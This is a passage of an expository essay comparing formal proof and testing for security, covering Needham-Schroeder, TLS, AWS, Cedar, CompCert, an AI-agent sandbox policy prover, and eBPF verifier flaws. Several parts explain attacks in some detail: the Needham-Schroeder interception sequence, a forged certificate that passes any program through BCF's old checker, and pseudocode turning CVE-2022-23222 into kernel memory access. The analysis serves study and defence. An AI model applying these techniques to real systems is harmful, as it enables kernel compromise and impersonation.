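2. Bob returns Na with a random number of his own, Nb, encrypted for Alice.
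3. Alice returns Nb, encrypted for Bob.

Only Bob could have read Na, and only Alice could have read Nb, so each seems to have good evidence of talking to the other.

Lowe, in *Breaking and Fixing the Needham-Schroeder Public-Key Protocol Using FDR*, modelled Alice, Bob and an intruder and gave the model to FDR, a model checker. The intruder can intercept any message, replay it without being able to read it, and compose new messages from known numbers. The intruder is also a legitimate user of the network, with whom Alice may choose to talk. One of Lowe's specifications was that Bob accepts a session with Alice only if Alice has started one with Bob. FDR found a run that breaks it:

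| Step | Sender | Recipient | Contents | Encrypted for |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Alice | Intruder | Na, Alice's name | Intruder |
| 2 | Intruder, posing as Alice | Bob | Na, Alice's name | Bob |
| 3 | Bob | Alice, but the intruder intercepts it | Na, Nb | Alice |
| 4 | Intruder | Alice | The message from step 3, still unread | Alice |
| 5 | Alice | Intruder | Nb | Intruder |
| 6 | Intruder, posing as Alice | Bob | Nb | Bob |

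The intruder can't read Bob's reply, so he forwards it to Alice. She expects a message containing Na and a new number, so she accepts it, decrypts it and sends the new number back to the intruder. Bob then believes he is talking to Alice, although she has never contacted him.

The fix is to put Bob's name in the second message. Alice, who thinks she is talking to the intruder, would then see the wrong name and stop. FDR found no attack on the corrected protocol in a small system where Alice and Bob could each take part in one run. An attack might still have been possible with more users or several runs at once, so Lowe proved by hand that any attack on a larger system would imply an attack on the small one.

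The flaw in this three-message protocol went unnoticed for 17 years, and Lowe notes that someone had published an incorrect proof about the protocol. Lowe had reported the attack in an earlier paper, so it is hard to tell how much the tool contributed to the original discovery. But the case shows that a checker with a fairly simple description of an intruder can find an attack that experts had missed.

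### TLS before and after release

TLS, the protocol that protects most web traffic, offers a rough comparison between analysis before and after release. Lawrence Paulson's *Inductive Analysis of the Internet Protocol TLS* (written in the 1990s and posted online in 2019) proved all the expected security goals of an early version and found no attacks, but researchers later found many weaknesses in TLS 1.2 and its predecessors.

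The proof had covered only the handshake, in which two computers agree on keys, and Paulson warned that the part carrying the application data needed examination too. The proof also assumed perfect encryption. Paulson (2022), in *Verifying cryptographic protocols, I*, defends this usual assumption, arguing that no protocol could be secure without it and that the attacks of interest bypass encryption. But after the proof, researchers recovered passwords from TLS traffic by exploiting statistical flaws in RC4, a cipher that TLS allowed. Others tested widely used TLS programs and found that some accepted messages in the wrong order, a fault in the code that a proof about the design can't reveal.

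Paterson and van der Merwe (2016), in *Reactive and Proactive Standardisation of TLS*, contrast this history with TLS 1.3, which researchers analysed before anyone deployed it. The designers went through 28 drafts, according to *It Takes a Village* (2025). One group used Tamarin, a protocol-analysis tool, to check draft 21 against its stated security requirements. They found a behaviour that weakened the authentication guarantees in some implementations, and their work strongly influenced the final version. Another group's analysis of draft 18 included a machine-checked proof in CryptoVerif, a tool that assesses the probability that an attacker with limited computing power could break the protocol, rather than assuming perfect encryption.

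A good reason to analyze a protocol early is that designers can fix an error in a draft by revising it, but fixing one after release means updating browsers and servers around the world. It's harder to say how much early analysis contributed to TLS 1.3's security, because the designers also knew about the attacks on earlier versions and set out to prevent them. Even a proof doesn't guarantee that a protocol is secure, since researchers broke the Wi-Fi protocol WPA2 after others had proved its handshake secure.

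### Amazon's rare failures

Engineers at Amazon Web Services, Amazon's cloud business, started using model checking in 2011 to find design errors that could lose customers' data when machines or networks fail. They wrote their specifications in TLA+, a language based on set theory and logic, or in PlusCal, which looks more like a programming language and translates into TLA+. *Use of Formal Methods at Amazon Web Services* (Newcombe, Rath and colleagues, 2014) gives details for six components, including parts of S3, which stores files; DynamoDB, a database; and EBS, which provides virtual disks.

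| Component | Lines of specification | Bugs found in the design |
|---|---|---|
| S3, network algorithm | 804 | 2, and more in proposed optimisations |
| S3, background redistribution of data | 645 | 1, and another in the first proposed fix |
| DynamoDB, replication and group membership | 939 | 3 |
| EBS, volume management | 102 | 3 |
| Lock manager, shared data structure | 223 | None |
| Lock manager, replication and reconfiguration | 318 | 1 |

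One of the DynamoDB bugs could lose data if certain failures and recovery steps interleaved with other work. The shortest sequence that triggered it had 35 steps. Tim Rath, who designed the mechanism, had already tested the code with simulated network faults, run long stress tests and written informal proofs. If a random test had three choices at every step, it would follow one particular 35-step path once in 3^35 (about 50 million billion) runs. Several paths may lead to the same bug, so the true odds are probably better. Amazon's engineers couldn't dismiss such a sequence as too unlikely to matter, because they had seen combinations of events at least as complicated in practice.

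In another case, several reviews missed a bug that surfaced only after months of testing. An engineer spent two weeks learning TLA+ and writing a specification, and the checker then found the bug in seconds. The checker also showed that the fix the team had already designed and reviewed didn't work. This is the closest the Amazon reports come to a direct comparison with testing, though the engineer already knew there was a bug.

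None of these bugs involved an attacker. *How Amazon Web Services Uses Formal Methods* (2015) lists the events in the models as network and disk errors, crashes, data-centre failures and the actions of human operators. The experience is still relevant to security, because a checker that tries every order of these events also tries any order an attacker might arrange. But an attacker can also forge messages, and a clean result covers forgery only if an engineer has added that ability to the model, as Lowe did.

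The check of the lock manager's data structure missed a bug that could stop the system from making progress, because nobody had set the checker to look for one. Newcombe and colleagues also told coworkers who asked that they had no way to know whether the code matched the checked design.

Amazon has since narrowed that gap. Brooker and Desai, in *Systems Correctness Practices at AWS*, describe PObserve, a 2023 tool that checks whether the specification allows the behaviour recorded in a running system's logs. The specifications are in P, a language that many Amazon programmers find easier than TLA+ because it describes a design as a set of communicating state machines. Engineers used P to remove several design bugs when they changed S3 so that a read always returns the latest write. Checking logs can expose a mismatch between code and design, but only in runs that have occurred.

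Brooker and Desai also describe work that involves an attacker. Firecracker, the software that runs customers' virtual machines, gives each machine simulated hardware, such as a disk or network card. A hostile customer can send any commands to this hardware, so Amazon's engineers proved that key properties of the code handling these commands hold whatever the customer's machine sends. Because proof takes much more work than model checking, they reserve it for boundaries like this one and for authorization, where they used it on the policy language Cedar.

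### No control group

Rath was convinced that more reviews and tests would not have found the 35-step bug. That is plausible, but no second team spent the same weeks on more testing for comparison. The reports also do not separate the benefit of the checker from the benefit of careful thought. Newcombe and colleagues observe that writing a precise design forces its author to think more clearly, and one of their specifications exposed ambiguities in a document without finding any bug. An engineer who spent two weeks writing a careful description in English might have caught some of the same errors.

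Successes are also more likely to be published. Newcombe and colleagues report that all seven teams using TLA+ found it highly valuable, but those teams had chosen to adopt it and kept using it. An engineer who gives up on a specification after a month has little reason to write an article about it. Published studies of protocols are subject to the same selection, since finding a flaw makes a better paper than finding nothing new.

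The study of key-storage devices is less prone to this problem because it reports how many devices resisted attack as well as how many failed. But the researchers didn't choose the 17 devices at random, so the nine failures don't give a failure rate for the market. Case reports can show that model checking finds serious flaws that reviewers and testers have missed, but engineers can't use them to predict how many flaws it will find in the next system, or how many the same money spent on more testing would have found.

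### Asking a solver about permission rules

The designs described so far change state as they process commands, so the checker has to search through sequences of commands. Permission rules are often simpler because they take one request and return a decision, but they are still hard to check because there may be infinitely many possible requests. An SMT solver, a program that either finds values that make a logical formula true or proves that none exist, can handle many such rules without trying the requests one by one.

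Suppose a company has two rules for its shared files:

1. Staff may read any file whose name begins with `reports/`.
2. Nobody may read a file whose name begins with `reports/pay`.

An engineer decides that the second rule should say `reports/payroll`, because payroll is what the company wants to protect. Tests with a payroll file and a sales report would give the right answers before and after the change. To find out whether the change opens anything up, the engineer asks the solver for a request r such that

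New(r) ∧ ¬Old(r),

which means that the new policy allows r and the old one forbids it. With the rules written out, the formula reduces to this: r comes from a member of staff, and the file's name begins with `reports/pay` but not with `reports/payroll`. The solver might answer with a request to read `reports/payments.csv`. If it had proved that no such request existed, the engineer would know that the new policy grants nothing the old one refused, for every possible file name. Swapping New and Old in the formula shows whether the change takes away access that somebody had.

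Amazon's Zelkova applies this method to the access policies that customers write for its cloud. It can compare two policies, or one policy with a general rule such as "no access for the public". It finds mistakes that customers made themselves, but an attacker who discovers an overly permissive rule can use it without breaking any software.

The use of AI agents to write policies is another reason to check them formally. Google's *Securing the agentic era* (2026) introduces a similar tool, built on the solver Z3, for policies in the company's Common Expression Language. It warns that an agent may fit a policy too closely to the existing tests, so that the policy passes them all but fails on other requests. Adding tests helps only until the agent fits the policy to those too.

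NVIDIA has applied the method to agents' permissions. Its OpenShell software runs each agent in a sandbox, a closed-off environment. According to NVIDIA, a supervisor outside the agent checks outgoing requests against a policy, and can let the agent read through a service but not write through it. The supervisor also holds the real passwords and keys, and supplies them only after a request passes its checks.

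The policy as a whole is harder to understand than any of its rules. *Policy Prover*, a guide to OpenShell's policy prover, gives the example of a file system that the owner has made read-only, but in which another setting attaches a writable folder. The prover translates the settings into constraints for Z3 and looks for values that would permit something dangerous. A code change proposed to OpenShell (2026) in April reduces the prover's task to checking whether data can leave the sandbox and whether the agent can write where its owner meant it only to read.

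In a draft change to OpenShell, developers also experimented with the query about old and new policies. The prover checks whether a proposed permission would let an agent reach anything it can't already reach, and the software scores the difference. A permission for one exact address could fit within a small budget, while one covering a wide range of addresses could trigger a review. The developers concluded that the approach works for the kinds of rule they had modelled, but marked the draft as not ready to merge.

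The published evidence for the prover is still limited. In the April change, the prover passed its seven tests and detected both a data leak and a way around a read-only rule in a sample policy. This shows that it works on an example, but not how often owners make such mistakes or how many attacks it would prevent. Its answers hold only if the supervisor enforces the policy correctly. Many useful agents need permission both to read private files and to send messages. For those agents, the prover will correctly report that data can leave, but the owner still has to decide which messages to allow.

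## Side-by-side comparisons of testing and proof

Amazon did not have a second team spend the same weeks on extra testing, so there is no way to know what that testing would have found. A few other projects come closer to a fair comparison. In one, researchers ran the same fuzzer on ordinary C compilers and on a compiler with a correctness proof. In each of two others, engineers used both proof and testing on a single piece of software and recorded how they found each bug.

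### One fuzzer, eleven compilers

A compiler translates human-readable code into machine instructions. Compilers are hard to test with random programs because nobody knows in advance what a random program should print. Yang, Chen and colleagues (2011) solved this with differential testing in *Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers*. Their tool, Csmith, generates a random C program that ends by printing a checksum of its variables. A script compiles the program with several compilers, runs each compiled version and compares the checksums. If two versions print the same checksum and a third prints a different one, the compiler that produced the third is probably wrong.

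The method works only if the program has a single correct result. The C standard lists 191 kinds of undefined behaviour, such as overflowing a signed integer, and 52 kinds where a compiler may choose among several options. Two correct compilers could produce different results for a program that depended on any of these. Csmith therefore analyses the code it generates as it goes, discards fragments that might be unsafe, and wraps risky arithmetic in checks.

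Over three years, Yang and colleagues reported about 325 compiler bugs, including 79 in GCC and 202 in LLVM, the two main open-source compilers. GCC's developers rated 25 of the GCC bugs serious enough to block a release. Each of the five commercial compilers crashed on some valid programs and silently mistranslated others within a few hours of testing.

When the researchers added random programs to the large existing test suites for GCC and LLVM, the tests ran hardly any more of the compilers' code. Many of the bugs must therefore have been in code that the old tests already ran, but only with inputs that it handled correctly.

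The eleventh compiler was CompCert, which handles a large subset of C. Its developers wrote most of it in Coq, a proof assistant (a program for writing and checking proofs). They proved that if CompCert successfully compiles a program that avoids undefined behaviour, the assembly code it produces behaves as the source program does.

Csmith still found bugs in it. One affected a function that returned the value of this expression, where `x` is an unsigned number:

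```
-1 <= (1 && x)
```

The part in brackets is always 0 or 1, so the comparison is true and the function should return 1. CompCert's version returned 0. An unsigned comparison would give that answer, because it reads the bits of −1 as 4,294,967,295. This bug and five like it were in the front end, which prepares the source program for the verified part of the compiler and had no proof at the time. Partly in response, CompCert's main developer extended the proof to cover such conversions.

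Two further bugs came from a gap in the specification. CompCert produced a PowerPC instruction to reserve 44,432 bytes of memory, but the instruction has only 16 bits for that number, which limits it to 32,768. CompCert's description of the processor omitted this limit, so the proof was about a slightly different machine from the real one. The assembler, the next tool in the chain, caught the error by rejecting the instruction. Csmith also made CompCert crash a handful of times.

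Csmith found no bugs in the middle of CompCert, where optimisations rewrite the program, though it had found bugs there in every other compiler it tested. By early 2011, after about six years of processor time, the development version of CompCert was the only compiler in which Csmith could find no mistranslations. By comparison, running a million random programs through 21 versions of GCC and LLVM took a little over two years of one core's time, spread over about a week and a half on 20 four-core machines.

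Size alone can't explain why Csmith found fewer bugs in CompCert than in GCC or LLVM. CompCert is much smaller and optimises less, so one would expect fewer bugs even without a proof, but Csmith broke every compiler without a proof, including the deliberately small TCC. A comparison within CompCert is stronger evidence. The same project produced the front end and the optimiser, and Csmith tested both. It found six mistranslations in the unproved front end and none in the proved optimiser, even though Yang and colleagues had designed it mainly to find bugs in optimisers.

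*A Systematic Impact Study for Fuzzer-Found Compiler Bugs* (2019) reports that intensive fuzzing had still found no bugs in CompCert's verified parts. The fuzzing used both Csmith and a technique that alters code a program never reaches on a given input and checks that the output stays the same. Testing continued to find many bugs in ordinary compilers. The method in *Skeletal Program Enumeration for Rigorous Compiler Testing* (2016), which systematically generates the programs that share a given structure, found more than 200 in GCC and Clang, LLVM's C compiler, in under six months.

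CompCert has had other bugs since 2011, some of which could silently produce wrong code. Monniaux and Boulmé (2022), in *The Trusted Computing Base of the CompCert Verified Compiler*, trace them to parts that the proof assumes are correct, most often the code that prints the final assembly instructions. They also examine Coq, in which developers have found about one critical bug a year. They think it highly unlikely that one of these bugs let a false theorem about CompCert through. CompCert's developers would have had to trigger the Coq bug by accident, in a way that looked innocent to anyone reading the proof, and the faulty optimisation would have had to fail so rarely that testing missed it.

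### Cedar, a proved model and a tested product

CompCert's developers proved theorems about the compiler itself. Amazon's engineers used a less laborious method for Cedar, a language for writing access rules. An application sends Cedar's authorizer a request, such as for an intern to create a task list, and the authorizer allows it if at least one rule permits it and no rule forbids it. A separate validator checks the rules before anyone relies on them. This check matters because the authorizer ignores any rule that causes an error. If an engineer mistyped `owner` as `pwner` in a rule that forbids an action, the rule would not block that action.

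Disselkoen, Eline and colleagues (2024), in *How We Built Cedar*, describe how they combined proof and testing:

1. They wrote a simple model of the authorizer and validator in Lean. It has about 1,700 lines, while the production code for the same components, in the language Rust, has about 11,600.
2. They proved theorems about the model. For example, a rule that forbids always overrides one that permits, every function eventually stops, and a rule that passes the validator never causes a type error (such as using a number where Cedar expects a name).
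3. They generated millions of random rules, data sets and requests, ran each through the model and the Rust code, and looked for different answers.
4. Where they had no model, they tested the Rust code for general properties. If a program prints a rule and reads it back in, for instance, it should get the same rule.

The theorems are about the Lean model, and only testing provides evidence that the Rust product matches it. Disselkoen and colleagues considered proving the Rust code correct, but judged that verification tools couldn't yet handle enough of the language. They also considered generating the product from the Lean model, but the resulting C code would have been hard to debug.

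They found four bugs while working on the proofs and 21 through testing:

| Method | Component | Bugs found |
|---|---|---|
| Proof | Validator | 4 |
| Differential testing against the model | Authorizer, including the code that evaluates rules | 6 |
| Differential testing against the model | Validator | 4 |
| Testing for general properties | Validator | 3 |
| Testing for general properties | Parser and formatter | 8 |

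Many of the disagreements between the model and the Rust code were about small details. They measured the length of a string differently, since length can be counted in bytes or characters, and "é" is one character but usually two bytes. The engineers decided that a string-length feature would confuse users and dropped it. In another case, the model wrongly rejected "::", which is a legitimate part of an internet address. The theorems about the model would not have exposed this error because none of them concerned address formats.

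The engineers used both methods on one property, that a validated policy never causes a type error. Random tests found three violations before the proof was complete, and the attempt to prove the property exposed three other bugs. The comparison is inexact because the tests examined the Rust code and the proof examined the model, but neither method made the other redundant. The proofs also exposed a fourth bug, an input that made the validator run forever. Lean requires a proof that each function stops, and the engineers found the bug when they couldn't supply one. Random tests had missed it because they were extremely unlikely to generate such an input.

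Disselkoen and colleagues also list nine bugs that their random tests missed, including the one that made the validator run forever. Three needed an input that the generators were unlikely to produce, three needed malformed input that the generators never produced, and three were in functions that no random test called. At least one, an error in the Rust code for the operator `in`, looks relevant to security because the operator determines whether a user belongs to a group. A theorem about the Lean model can't reveal a mistake in the Rust code, so neither method caught this bug. Trying to prove the Rust code correct would have exposed it, if the specification covered group membership.

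Better generators would catch some of these bugs, but it is hard to tell how good a generator is. One of Cedar's generators reached every line of the code under test, a common standard of thoroughness, yet many of its inputs exercised only the code that handles errors. In a typical run of another generator, 35.5% of the conditions it produced were just "true" or "false", which tests very little. A new generator reduced this to 9.7%.

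### Keel and the checker it replaces

The third comparison concerns BCF, the extension that lets a Linux user submit a proof when the eBPF verifier would reject a safe program. For the program with the 800-byte buffer, the verifier misses the relation between the second record's start, n, and its greatest length, 800 − n. The user's proof supplies it:

1. The second record ends, at the latest, at byte n + (800 − n).
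2. That sum equals 800.
3. So the record can't end after byte 800, which contradicts the verifier's formula for an unsafe write.

The second step depends on a rule for simplifying sums. Cai and colleagues found that BCF's original checker never did the simplification. It accepted whatever equation the user wrote, so it would also have accepted n + (800 − n) = 5. On the programs from BCF's own evaluation, it left 7.2% of the proof steps unchecked in this way.

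Another bug was harder to spot. The checker had a rule for comparing two products that share a factor:

y·a < x·a if and only if y ≠ x, a ≠ 0, and (y < x) ↔ (a > 0).

The last part means that "y < x" and "a > 0" are both true or both false. The rule is correct for ordinary whole numbers, because multiplying by a positive number preserves their order and multiplying by a negative number reverses it. But a computer stores numbers in a fixed number of bits. Eight bits can hold signed numbers from −128 to 127, and a result outside that range wraps around.

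When y = 64, x = 0 and a = 2, the product 64 × 2 should be 128, but its eight bits are 10000000, which the computer reads as −128. The left side of the rule is then −128 < 0, which is true. On the right, 64 < 0 is false while 2 > 0 is true, so the last part fails and the whole right side is false. The two sides are therefore not equivalent, and the rule is wrong for these values.

An attacker can turn this into a proof of anything:

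1. Apply the rule to these three numbers, which gives "left side if and only if right side".
2. Calculate the left side, which is true. By step 1, the right side must be true as well.
3. Calculate the right side, which is false.
4. This is a contradiction, so declare the verifier's formula impossible.

The argument never uses the verifier's formula. Cai and colleagues wrote it out as a 13-step certificate, and the old checker accepted it as a refutation of every formula they tried, including one that is always true. The verifier treats a refutation as proof that the unsafe access can't happen, so an attacker could attach the same certificate to any program and get it past any safety check that the verifier refers to the checker. The researchers confirmed the danger in a running kernel, using a certificate forged through a different faulty rule. The kernel loaded the programs carrying it when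 it used the old checker, but refused them when it used Keel. Keel's version of the product rule also requires enough bits to hold the exact product, which means 16 bits for two 8-bit numbers.

### How the researchers found the 13 bugs

Cai and colleagues discovered the faulty product rule when they tried to prove it sound in Lean and couldn't. They found only one other bug this way. The supplement to their paper records how they found all 13:

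| How they found it | Bugs | Example |
|---|---|---|
| A failed proof, and later fuzzing as well | 2 | The product rule |
| Reading the code, but not fuzzing | 6 | A search that could write past the end of an array |
| Both reading the code and fuzzing | 3 | A crash on a reference to a term that doesn't exist |
| Fuzzing, but not reading the code | 2 | A rule that ignored the order in which two strings of bits are joined |

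The researchers had AI tools read the code and compare it with Keel's specification. For the fuzzing, they altered existing certificates and ran about 64 million of them through both checkers in four half-hour campaigns. Since they had proved Keel sound, any step that only the old checker accepted either revealed a bug in the old checker or was a valid step that Keel didn't support. They examined each of these steps by hand.

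The faulty array search shows how fuzzing can miss a bug that is easy to see by reading the code. The array had room for 64 entries, but the code checked against a limit of 128. A certificate triggers the bug only if it contains a formula nested more than 64 levels deep, which random alterations are unlikely to produce. A reader only has to notice that the two numbers differ. An attacker could have used the bug to overwrite kernel memory, though with the compiler protection that BCF's configuration turns on, the machine would halt instead.

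Fuzzing, in turn, found two bugs that the readers had missed. One was in a rule for rearranging formulas that treated joining x to y as the same as joining y to x. With 8-bit numbers, joining 1 to 0 gives 256, but joining 0 to 1 gives 1. The other was a crash in the code that writes error messages, which may be easy to overlook when comparing a checker's logical rules with a specification.

Keel did not crash, hang or leak memory on any of the 64 million certificates. Its speed advantage over the old checker grows with certificate size. About 98.6% of certificates take 12 to 13 microseconds with either checker. For the rest, which are larger, the median is 55 microseconds with Keel and 110 with the old checker. Most of this speed comes from storing only one copy of each formula, which lets Keel check whether two formulas are the same by comparing two numbers. An unverified checker could do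 the same, so the speed is not a benefit of the proof. Users would hardly notice the difference, because the checker accounts for at most about 1% of program loading time.

### Why the bug counts don't rank the methods

By bug count, testing looks far more productive than proof, which accounts for only four of Cedar's 25 bugs and two of Keel's 13. Fuzzing also rediscovered both bugs that had surfaced in Keel's failed proofs, so a good fuzzer might have been enough to find them. But engineers write proofs mainly for assurance, and only the finished proof shows that Keel's other rules are free of similar mistakes.

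The counts also depend on the condition of the software. Alastair Donaldson, a computer scientist at Imperial College London, worked on formal methods for twelve years before turning mainly to fuzzing. In *From Formal Methods to Fuzzing and Back*, Donaldson (2026) observes that the number of bugs a fuzzer finds depends as much on how reliable the software already was, and how heavily others had fuzzed it, as on the quality of the fuzzer. The old eBPF checker was part of a research project, and its developers distributed it as a set of changes to Linux. We can't infer from thirteen bugs in such a checker how many a similar effort would find in code that thousands of companies have used for years.

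The kinds of bug each method found are more informative than the totals. Proof attempts exposed errors in a design's logic that only unusual inputs would reveal, such as a multiplication that wraps around or a validator that never stops. Tests did better where a description might not match what it describes, as with a processor's instruction format, a string's length, or a parser.

Testing and proof both need a way to tell a right answer from a wrong one, which testers call the oracle problem. Donaldson argues that this problem links fuzzing to formal methods. Yang and colleagues could avoid writing a specification of C because they had eleven compilers to compare, but the maker of a new guard usually has no other guard to compare it with. In Cedar and Keel, a formal specification served as the oracle, and much of its value came through testing. It accounts for ten of the 21 bugs that tests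 found in Cedar, and for the disagreements that the fuzzer found between Keel and the old checker. An engineer who writes a precise, executable specification can therefore benefit from it before proving anything.

These three projects are a small and unusual sample. Compilers, authorizers and proof checkers all have correct outputs that can be defined exactly in mathematics. Verification specialists built all three proved systems and chose which parts to prove. Disselkoen and colleagues did not model Cedar's parser, partly because it was unclear what they could prove about it, yet parsers are a common source of security bugs. The people who built Cedar and Keel also counted the bugs in them, so only CompCert had outside testers. None of the projects gave two teams the same budget and compared the results.

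Such comparisons also require a finished proof, so they leave out software that nobody has managed to verify. Donaldson moved to fuzzing largely because it worked on industrial programs with millions of lines of code, while formal methods were hard to scale. Fuzzers have found hundreds of bugs in GCC and LLVM, but no one has proved either compiler correct, so we can't know what a proof would have added.

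## Vulnerability records and attack exercises: eBPF and seL4

A record of past flaws can cover any software that people use and repair, unlike the comparisons for Cedar and Keel. eBPF has a long record of flaws, and only parts of eBPF have proofs. seL4, a small operating-system kernel, has one of the most complete proofs of any working system, and professional attackers have tried to break into aircraft that run it.

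### Ten years of eBPF flaws

Chen and colleagues collected 11,388 records from 2016 to 2025. The records came from fixes to the Linux kernel's source code, reports from syzbot (a service that continuously fuzzes the kernel), and the US National Vulnerability Database, which lists publicly disclosed flaws under CVE numbers. Scripts discarded records that did not concern eBPF, and two researchers independently judged the doubtful ones. If several records pointed to the same fix, the researchers counted them once. They checked 600 of the remaining records and found that 96.7% were correct.

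The final dataset has 2,766 flaws, of which 88% came from kernel fixes, 7% from the vulnerability database and 5% from syzbot. A count of public disclosures would have missed most of them. Chen and colleagues selected the kernel fixes by the files each fix changed and the wording of its description. These criteria don't show that an attacker could have exploited each flaw, so the dataset is probably best read as a list of eBPF flaws that developers thought worth fixing.

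The main breakdown by component covers 2,234 of them:

| Part of eBPF | Flaws | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Runtime | 1,577 | 70.6% |
| Verifier | 389 | 17.4% |
| JIT compiler | 151 | 6.8% |
| User-space tools | 117 | 5.2% |

In another table in the same study, which covers the full 2,766, 67% are in the runtime and 19% in the verifier. The totals don't match, but the components rank in the same order.

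The researchers examined a sample of 642 flaws to find their causes. The largest group was 135 concurrency faults, in which operations running at the same time interfere with each other. Another 100 were faults elsewhere in the kernel that eBPF had made reachable. In one of these, an eBPF program could call a kernel function to shrink a network packet. The code that released the leftover memory could handle only ordinary memory, so it crashed the kernel if the packet was in a special shared buffer. The verifier correctly accepted such programs because it checks the program, not the kernel code that the program calls.

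### A verifier failure and a JIT failure

The eBPF verifier depends on an invariant, which is a condition that must hold throughout a run. The values the verifier records for a register must always include the register's real value. The flaw CVE-2022-23222 violated this invariant.

A program can ask the kernel to reserve space in a ring buffer, a queue for passing data to other software. The kernel returns the address of the space, or 0 if it can't reserve any. Until the program has checked for 0, the verifier should forbid arithmetic on the result. It had a list of pointer types to which this ban applied, but nobody had added the type for ring buffers, which arrived in Linux 5.8. The verifier allowed arithmetic on any type not on the list, so it accepted this:

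```
r0 = reserve space      (an address, or 0)
r1 = r0
r1 = r1 + 1
if r0 is 0:             the verifier records r1 as 0, but r1 is really 1
```

The verifier had labelled r1 as a copy of r0, so on the branch where r0 was 0 it recorded 0 for r1 as well. An attacker can enlarge this error by multiplying r1 by any number they choose, such as 5,000. The real value is then 5,000, but the verifier still calculates 0. The program can then add r1 to the address of a small buffer, and the verifier will approve an access that lands 5,000 bytes away. Attackers could use the flaw to read and write arbitrary kernel memory.

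The JIT compiler has a different invariant, that the machine code does exactly what the approved bytecode does. The bug recorded as CVE-2025-22048 broke this invariant on computers with LoongArch processors. There, the JIT compiler uses register a5 for the result of an eBPF function, but ordinary kernel functions return their results in a0. The compiler therefore added an instruction after every call to copy a0 into a5. This is correct after a call to a kernel function, but when one part of an eBPF program calls another, the result is already in a5, and the copy overwrote it. In one of the kernel's tests, the overwritten result was a memory address, so the next instruction read from the wrong place and the kernel crashed.

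The verifier had correctly approved the bytecode in that test, so proving the verifier correct would not have prevented the crash. Proving the JIT compiler correct might have, if the proof had covered LoongArch.

### What three days of fuzzing reached

Chen and colleagues also ran Syzkaller, the fuzzer behind syzbot, on Linux 5.10, a version for which their dataset has 514 flaws. Syzkaller generates sequences of requests to the kernel and keeps the ones that reach new code. In 72 hours on eight virtual machines, it ran about 140 million test programs and kept 4,165. Only 642 of those tried to load an eBPF program, and only 368 got one past the verifier.

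The fuzzer reached 22% of the basic blocks (short runs of instructions without a branch) in the eBPF code, including 34% of those in the verifier, 27% in the JIT compiler and 17% in the runtime. These figures overstate how thoroughly it tested the code, because more than 90% of the inputs that tried to load a program used only two program types. eBPF has many types, for jobs such as filtering packets or tracing the kernel, and the verifier applies different rules to each.

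Syzkaller triggered about 290 crashes of three kinds, all because one thread used a ring buffer while another closed it and freed its memory. It found no bugs in the verifier or the JIT compiler.

One reason is that a wrong verdict from the verifier doesn't crash anything by itself. In the ring-buffer example, r1 can hold 1 when the verifier has recorded 0, and the kernel will keep running until the program uses r1 to access the wrong memory. This is another case of the oracle problem. A draft tool presented at the Linux Plumbers Conference in 2025 would help by saving the values the verifier calculates for each register and comparing them with the real values as the program runs. The first version works only when the kernel interprets the bytecode instead of compiling it.

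Finding one cause, compared with the 514 flaws in the dataset, isn't a fair measure of what fuzzing can do. The campaign lasted only three days and ran on x86 machines, where flaws specific to other processors couldn't appear. Specialised fuzzers may also do better. Chen and colleagues judged from BRF's design that it can test parts of the runtime effectively because it generates valid programs. Another fuzzer, Buzzer, can detect one kind of wrong verdict from the verifier. In their judgement, none of the three fuzzers covers JIT errors specific to one processor, like the LoongArch flaw.

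### Harmful programs that the verifier rightly accepts

A program can obey all of the verifier's rules and still do harm. *HEIMDALL* (Dasu, Santra and colleagues, 2026) reports nine bugs in real eBPF programs that the verifier accepts. The Heimdall tool translates eBPF programs from C to Rust, whose compiler catches more mistakes. A language model writes the translation, and a solver looks for an input on which the two versions behave differently. The solver proved that no such input exists for 109 of 115 programs, assuming that calls to the kernel succeed and that uninitialized memory reads as zero. If the versions differ, either the translation is wrong or the Rust version has corrected a bug in the original, so the search also exposes old bugs.

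The worst bug was in filetop, a program that reports which files are in use. It copies each file's name out of kernel memory, but it always copied 4,096 bytes, the full size of its own buffer. Most names are much shorter, so it also copied the memory next to them, including addresses that reveal where the kernel is in memory. Linux randomises that location to make attacks harder. The verifier confirmed that the buffer had room for 4,096 bytes, but it could not check the size of the copy against the length of the name, which the bytecode does not show.

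A second program, bashreadline, which reports the commands that users type, also leaked kernel addresses. It sent an 84-byte record even when a short command had filled only part of it. Linux deliberately lets sufficiently privileged users load programs that read uninitialized memory. Katran, which distributes network traffic for Meta, used `=` where it needed `==`, so it overwrote a value instead of testing it. Developers have fixed eight of the nine bugs.

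The flaws described so far need different remedies:

| Flaw | The verifier's verdict | What a proof would have to cover |
|---|---|---|
| Arithmetic on a ring-buffer pointer | Wrong | The verifier's rules for pointers |
| Overwritten result on LoongArch | Right | The JIT compiler |
| Crash when shrinking a packet | Right | The kernel function that the program calls |
| Oversized copy in filetop | Right | The program itself, under a rule against leaking memory |

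The check itself was wrong only for the ring-buffer pointer. The other flaws were outside what the check covered, so even a flawless verifier would have missed them.

Trusted developers introduced the bugs in the nine programs by accident, so Heimdall's results do not measure what a hostile programmer could get past the verifier. An outsider could still exploit some of the bugs. In bashreadline, for example, an ordinary user could control how much memory leaked by typing shorter or longer commands.

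### Proving the verifier's arithmetic

Agni, a tool developed mainly at Rutgers University, proves part of the verifier correct. It covers the code that works out which values a register can hold. If r1 is between 2 and 6 and the program adds 10, for example, the verifier should record a range of 12 to 16. Suppose the verifier has recorded the sets A and B for two registers, and calculates the set G(A, B) for the result of an operation f. The calculation is sound if

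for all x in A and y in B, f(x, y) is in G(A, B).

Agni extracts the relevant functions from the kernel's C code, turns them into a logical formula and uses the solver Z3 to search for a case that breaks this condition. Because it works from the source code itself, the researchers can run it again whenever the kernel changes. Vishwanathan, Shachnai and colleagues report in *Agni* that the tool ran daily on three development versions of Linux in 2024. Rutgers' *Verifying the eBPF Verifier in the Linux Kernel with Agni* describes it as part of the kernel's continuous integration, the automatic checks that run as developers change the code.

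Agni needed 2.5 hours for Linux 4.14, 36 hours for 6.3 and several weeks for 6.4, and it ran out of time on 6.5. The main cause of the slowdown was a shared routine that runs after every operation to reconcile the verifier's different records of a register. As developers made this routine more sophisticated, the formulas grew. To address this, the researchers proved the routine and the individual operations separately. This works only if each piece is sound by itself, and some of the operations weren't, so the researchers fixed them in Linux 6.10.

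*Detecting Empty Abstractions and Pruning Dead Paths in the Linux eBPF Verifier* (Vishwanathan, Narayana and Nagarakatte, 2026) reports that Agni has proved the verifier's arithmetic and branching rules sound for versions up to an early release of Linux 7.1. A proof of the whole verifier is still a goal. Agni would not have caught the ring-buffer flaw, which concerned pointer types.

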